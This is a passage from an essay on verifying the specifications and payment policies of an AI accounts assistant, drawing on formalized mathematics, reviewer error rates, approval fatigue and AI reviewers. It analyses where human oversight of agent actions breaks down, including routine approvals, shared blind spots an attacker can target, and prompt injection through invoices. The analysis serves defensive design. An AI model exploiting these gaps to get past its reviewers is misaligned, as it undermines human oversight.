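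Reviewers with the same training often miss the same things, which makes these figures too optimistic. Suppose one error in five is of a kind that nobody at the company would notice, such as a missing "always". Let each reviewer catch the other kinds with probability 0.875, which still comes to 70% of all errors. Two reviewers now catch any given error with probability

**0.8 × (1 − 0.125²) ≈ 0.79,**

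and they find all ten only about 9% of the time. However many reviewers the company adds, the chance can't rise above 0.8¹⁰, or 11%. An attacker who knows the blind spot can also put every error there, and then the reviewers will find none of them.

### Forty years in print

Mathematics offers an unusual chance to see what careful readers miss. About 100 mathematicians proved the classification of finite simple groups, a complete list of the building blocks of finite symmetry, in more than 500 articles totaling about 15,000 pages. Axiom's *Formalizing the Enormous Theorem* (2026) describes the company's effort to rewrite the proof in Lean, with staff directing dozens of AI agents.

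Most of the problems they found were minor, such as misprints, wrong entries in tables and missing hypotheses. But in 34 places, or about once every 440 pages, they had to depart notably from the published record. The most serious case concerned the Unbalanced Group Theorem, a key step in the classification. *The Unbalanced Group Theorem* (Cook, 2026) explains that Axiom found counterexamples to an assertion on which the theorem's 1986 proof depends. The theorem is still true, and *The Classification of Finite Simple Groups, formalized in Lean* (Cureton, Ilin and colleagues) describes a different proof.

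These numbers show that a false step can survive for four decades in a proof on which other work depends. They do not give a detection rate, because nobody knows how many errors authors and referees removed before publication. The classification survived because mathematicians could repair the argument. A company can't always repair the effects of a faulty program, since the money may be gone before anyone finds the fault. The mathematicians' errors were also honest mistakes that nobody had hidden.

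### Approval fatigue

AgentSpec, Progent and FIDES can all prompt a user to approve an action that the software won't allow on its own. This works only if the user reads the request. People who see many harmless requests tend to start approving them automatically, which is called approval fatigue. Psychologists have found a related effect in visual searches, such as looking for weapons in luggage scans, where people miss a larger share of targets when targets are rare.

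Suppose the accounts assistant sends a manager 100 approval requests a day, and one in 2,000 is malicious. At a minute per request, the manager will read for more than 33 hours, spread over 20 working days, to find one malicious request. Siu and colleagues' participants leaned towards approval even though half of their cases were invalid. A manager whose last 1,999 approvals were all correct has much more reason than they did to expect the next request to be fine.

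The most promising remedy is to ask the manager for approval less often. Progent needed approval for only 6% of its policy updates. If the company could likewise let 94% of the assistant's requests through automatically, the manager would see six a day and do about two hours of reading for each bad request among them, provided the filter never let a bad one through. Even so, a manager may not stay attentive through months of routine requests.

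Approval requests also work better when they describe something the user can judge. A manager can understand "Pay Acme 400, to a different account from last month" in a few seconds, but will probably approve or refuse a 200-line script without reading it.

### Short statements in place of long code

A reviewer can read a program's specification and let a checker verify that the program meets it. On November 20, 2026, Levent Alpöge released a proof of the Riemann hypothesis, a famous problem about prime numbers, in 17 million lines of Lean. The Lean and Mathlib communities' *Lean verification of the Riemann Hypothesis* (2026) certified it the next day, before anyone could have read it all.

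Reviewers didn't need to catch subtle errors in Alpöge's library. Mathlib, Lean's main library of mathematics, already contained a statement of the hypothesis that experts had vetted. Volunteers put that statement in a separate file that used only Mathlib, and two independent tools confirmed that Alpöge's library proved exactly the same statement. Without this check, a definition somewhere in the 17 million lines could have given a familiar name to an easier theorem. Several proof checkers then accepted the proof, including two that have been formally proved never to accept a false one.

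Experts took a similar approach to OpenAI's proof about Yang–Mills theory, which describes forces between particles. According to Mint's *AI has proved that a theory underpinning fundamental physics is trustworthy*, five physicists checked that the Lean version matched the problem. They did not claim to fully understand the 1,147-page proof in ordinary language.

The theorem that Axiom proved takes only a few lines to state, but Xena reports that those lines depend on about 5,600 lines of definitions, including definitions of the sporadic groups, the 26 exceptions that belong to no infinite family. Buzzard had not met anyone who claimed to have checked the definitions carefully, and he considers the proof by far the best evidence that they are right. If a definition described the wrong group, the real one would probably be missing from the list, and the theorem would be false. A successful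 proof gives no such evidence that a payment policy is right, because a policy that is too loose is easier to satisfy.

Readers also have to check the statement, however short it is. In October 2026 OpenAI released Lean code with 290 of its mathematical results, and in about 38 cases the code does not state the paper's main theorem. One of these papers claims to prove Lech's multiplicity conjecture, open since 1960, but the main theorem in its Lean code is only a corollary from the paper. OpenAI never said that the code covered everything, but a reader who took the presence of Lean code as confirmation of the main result would be mistaken in those cases.

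For the accounts assistant, the list of operations in its library, with their types, is the equivalent of a theorem's statement. A reviewer can read pay(supplier, amount) once instead of reading every program that calls it. The reviewer must then find out what counts as a supplier and who can add one, since what the operation allows depends mostly on those definitions.

### Examples and counterexamples

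Software can turn a rule into concrete cases, which are easier to judge. A program that tried small numbers in Buzzard's version of Fermat's Last Theorem would immediately find the problem with zero. If somebody tried Meijer's file-deleting workflow in a folder with a third text file, they would see that file deleted.

Examples can also reveal that a rule allows more than it seems to. One of Greenman and colleagues' formulas required that whenever a red light is on, it is off at the next step and on again at the step after that. Eight answers described a light that blinks forever, but a light that never comes on also satisfies the formula. Greenman and colleagues think people might have avoided this mistake if the question had also asked for one sequence that fits the formula and one that doesn't.

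Siu and colleagues suggest showing example runs beside a specification. They also suggest having reviewers choose the valid specification from several, since people who have to compare options can't just approve the one in front of them. They did not test either idea. Under Ammann's programme, tools would show reviewers edge cases, counterexamples and hidden assumptions.

A reviewer who would never notice that a formula lacks a daily limit can easily see that "pay Acme 900, fifty times today" is wrong. But a tool has to find that example among millions of harmless ones, and it can't identify which examples matter unless it has something to compare them with, such as an older version of the policy. Developers should therefore have the tool search for extremes, such as the largest total the policy allows in a day.

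### Writing the specification twice

Two people can also independently translate the same English requirement into logic. A solver can then compare the two versions, as Cedar's analyser does with old and new policies.

Greenman and colleagues did not try this, but their results allow a rough estimate. The researchers got 28% of their formulas wrong, so two authors who made mistakes independently would both be wrong about 8% of the time. Even then, the solver would detect a problem whenever their mistakes differed. But seven of the researchers' roughly 16 wrong answers involved a missing "always". If both authors leave out the same "always", their formulas will be equivalent and the solver will find no difference.

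The method is better at exposing ambiguous English. One question included the phrase "Blue will turn on". Greenman and colleagues meant that the blue light is on now or will be later, while some students reasonably took it to mean that the light is off at first and then comes on. A solver would find the difference, and both authors would go back to whoever wrote the requirement. The solver can't find something the requirement leaves out, such as the instruction to keep all the other files, because both authors start from the same text.

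### AI reviewers

An AI reviewer does not get bored after 1,999 harmless requests, and it can read far more than any person. In Anthropic's project on Fermat's Last Theorem, Claude agents wrote the intermediate statements, checked one another's statements and proved them. People contributed only the one-line statement of the goal, plus occasional encouragement and comments on priorities.

The AI reviewers helped keep a very large project on course, but the result did not depend on their judgement. If they had approved a useless intermediate statement, the agents would have wasted some work, but Lean would still have rejected any proof that failed to reach the goal. A company that asks AI to review its payment policy has no such safeguard, because the policy itself defines the goal and there is no separate goal to check it against.

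Testa (2026) warned in *Maintaining a Large Formalization Project 2*, a set of lecture slides from March, that definitions and statements written by AI are more likely than human ones to differ from what people intended, but said that people tend to notice quickly. This seems to conflict with Siu and colleagues' results, but mathematicians who read a definition in their own field already know what it should say, whereas Siu and colleagues' participants were judging unfamiliar rules for an unfamiliar game. The accounts company should therefore have its policy reviewed by somebody who knows how it pays its bills, even if that person needs help with the notation. Models have improved since March, so Testa's warning may be less true now.

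AI reviewers can share blind spots too, especially if the same model wrote the work and reviews it. Claude looked for bugs in its own rewrite of Bun, but 19 regressions still got through. An AI reviewer may also follow malicious instructions hidden in an invoice it reads. AI reviewers can safely raise extra objections, as long as their approval never replaces a check in code.

An AI reviewer's objections may be most useful as warnings to people. The code-review experiment suggests that developers are more likely to find a flaw when they know one is there, and an AI reviewer can point to a particular line. But if most of its warnings are false, people will stop checking them carefully, as happens with approval fatigue.

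### What a restricted language changes

A restricted language makes some errors impossible. If `pay` accepts only listed suppliers, reviewers don't have to check for programs that pass it an account number from an invoice. Suppose the restrictions leave three errors out of ten. A reviewer who notices each error with probability 0.7 would find all three 34% of the time, compared with 3% for all ten. Two such reviewers working independently would together find all three 75% of the time.

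Some of the remaining errors are also easier to find, because words such as `endorse`, `@assumeSafe` and `unsafe` mark the exceptions to the rules. The reviewer still has to decide whether each exception is justified. The people who know the business best may even find a policy in temporal logic harder to judge than ordinary code. If a list of suppliers and a daily limit are enough, the company has good reason to use them instead of a formula.

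Other errors move to places where they affect more. A mistake in one program might cause one wrong payment, but a mistake in the policy applies to every program the assistant writes. Errors can also move from the code into the data. If somebody types the wrong account number into the supplier list, the compiler, the policy and the proof won't catch it. A reviewer can't find the mistake by reading any of them either, so somebody has to call the supplier to check.
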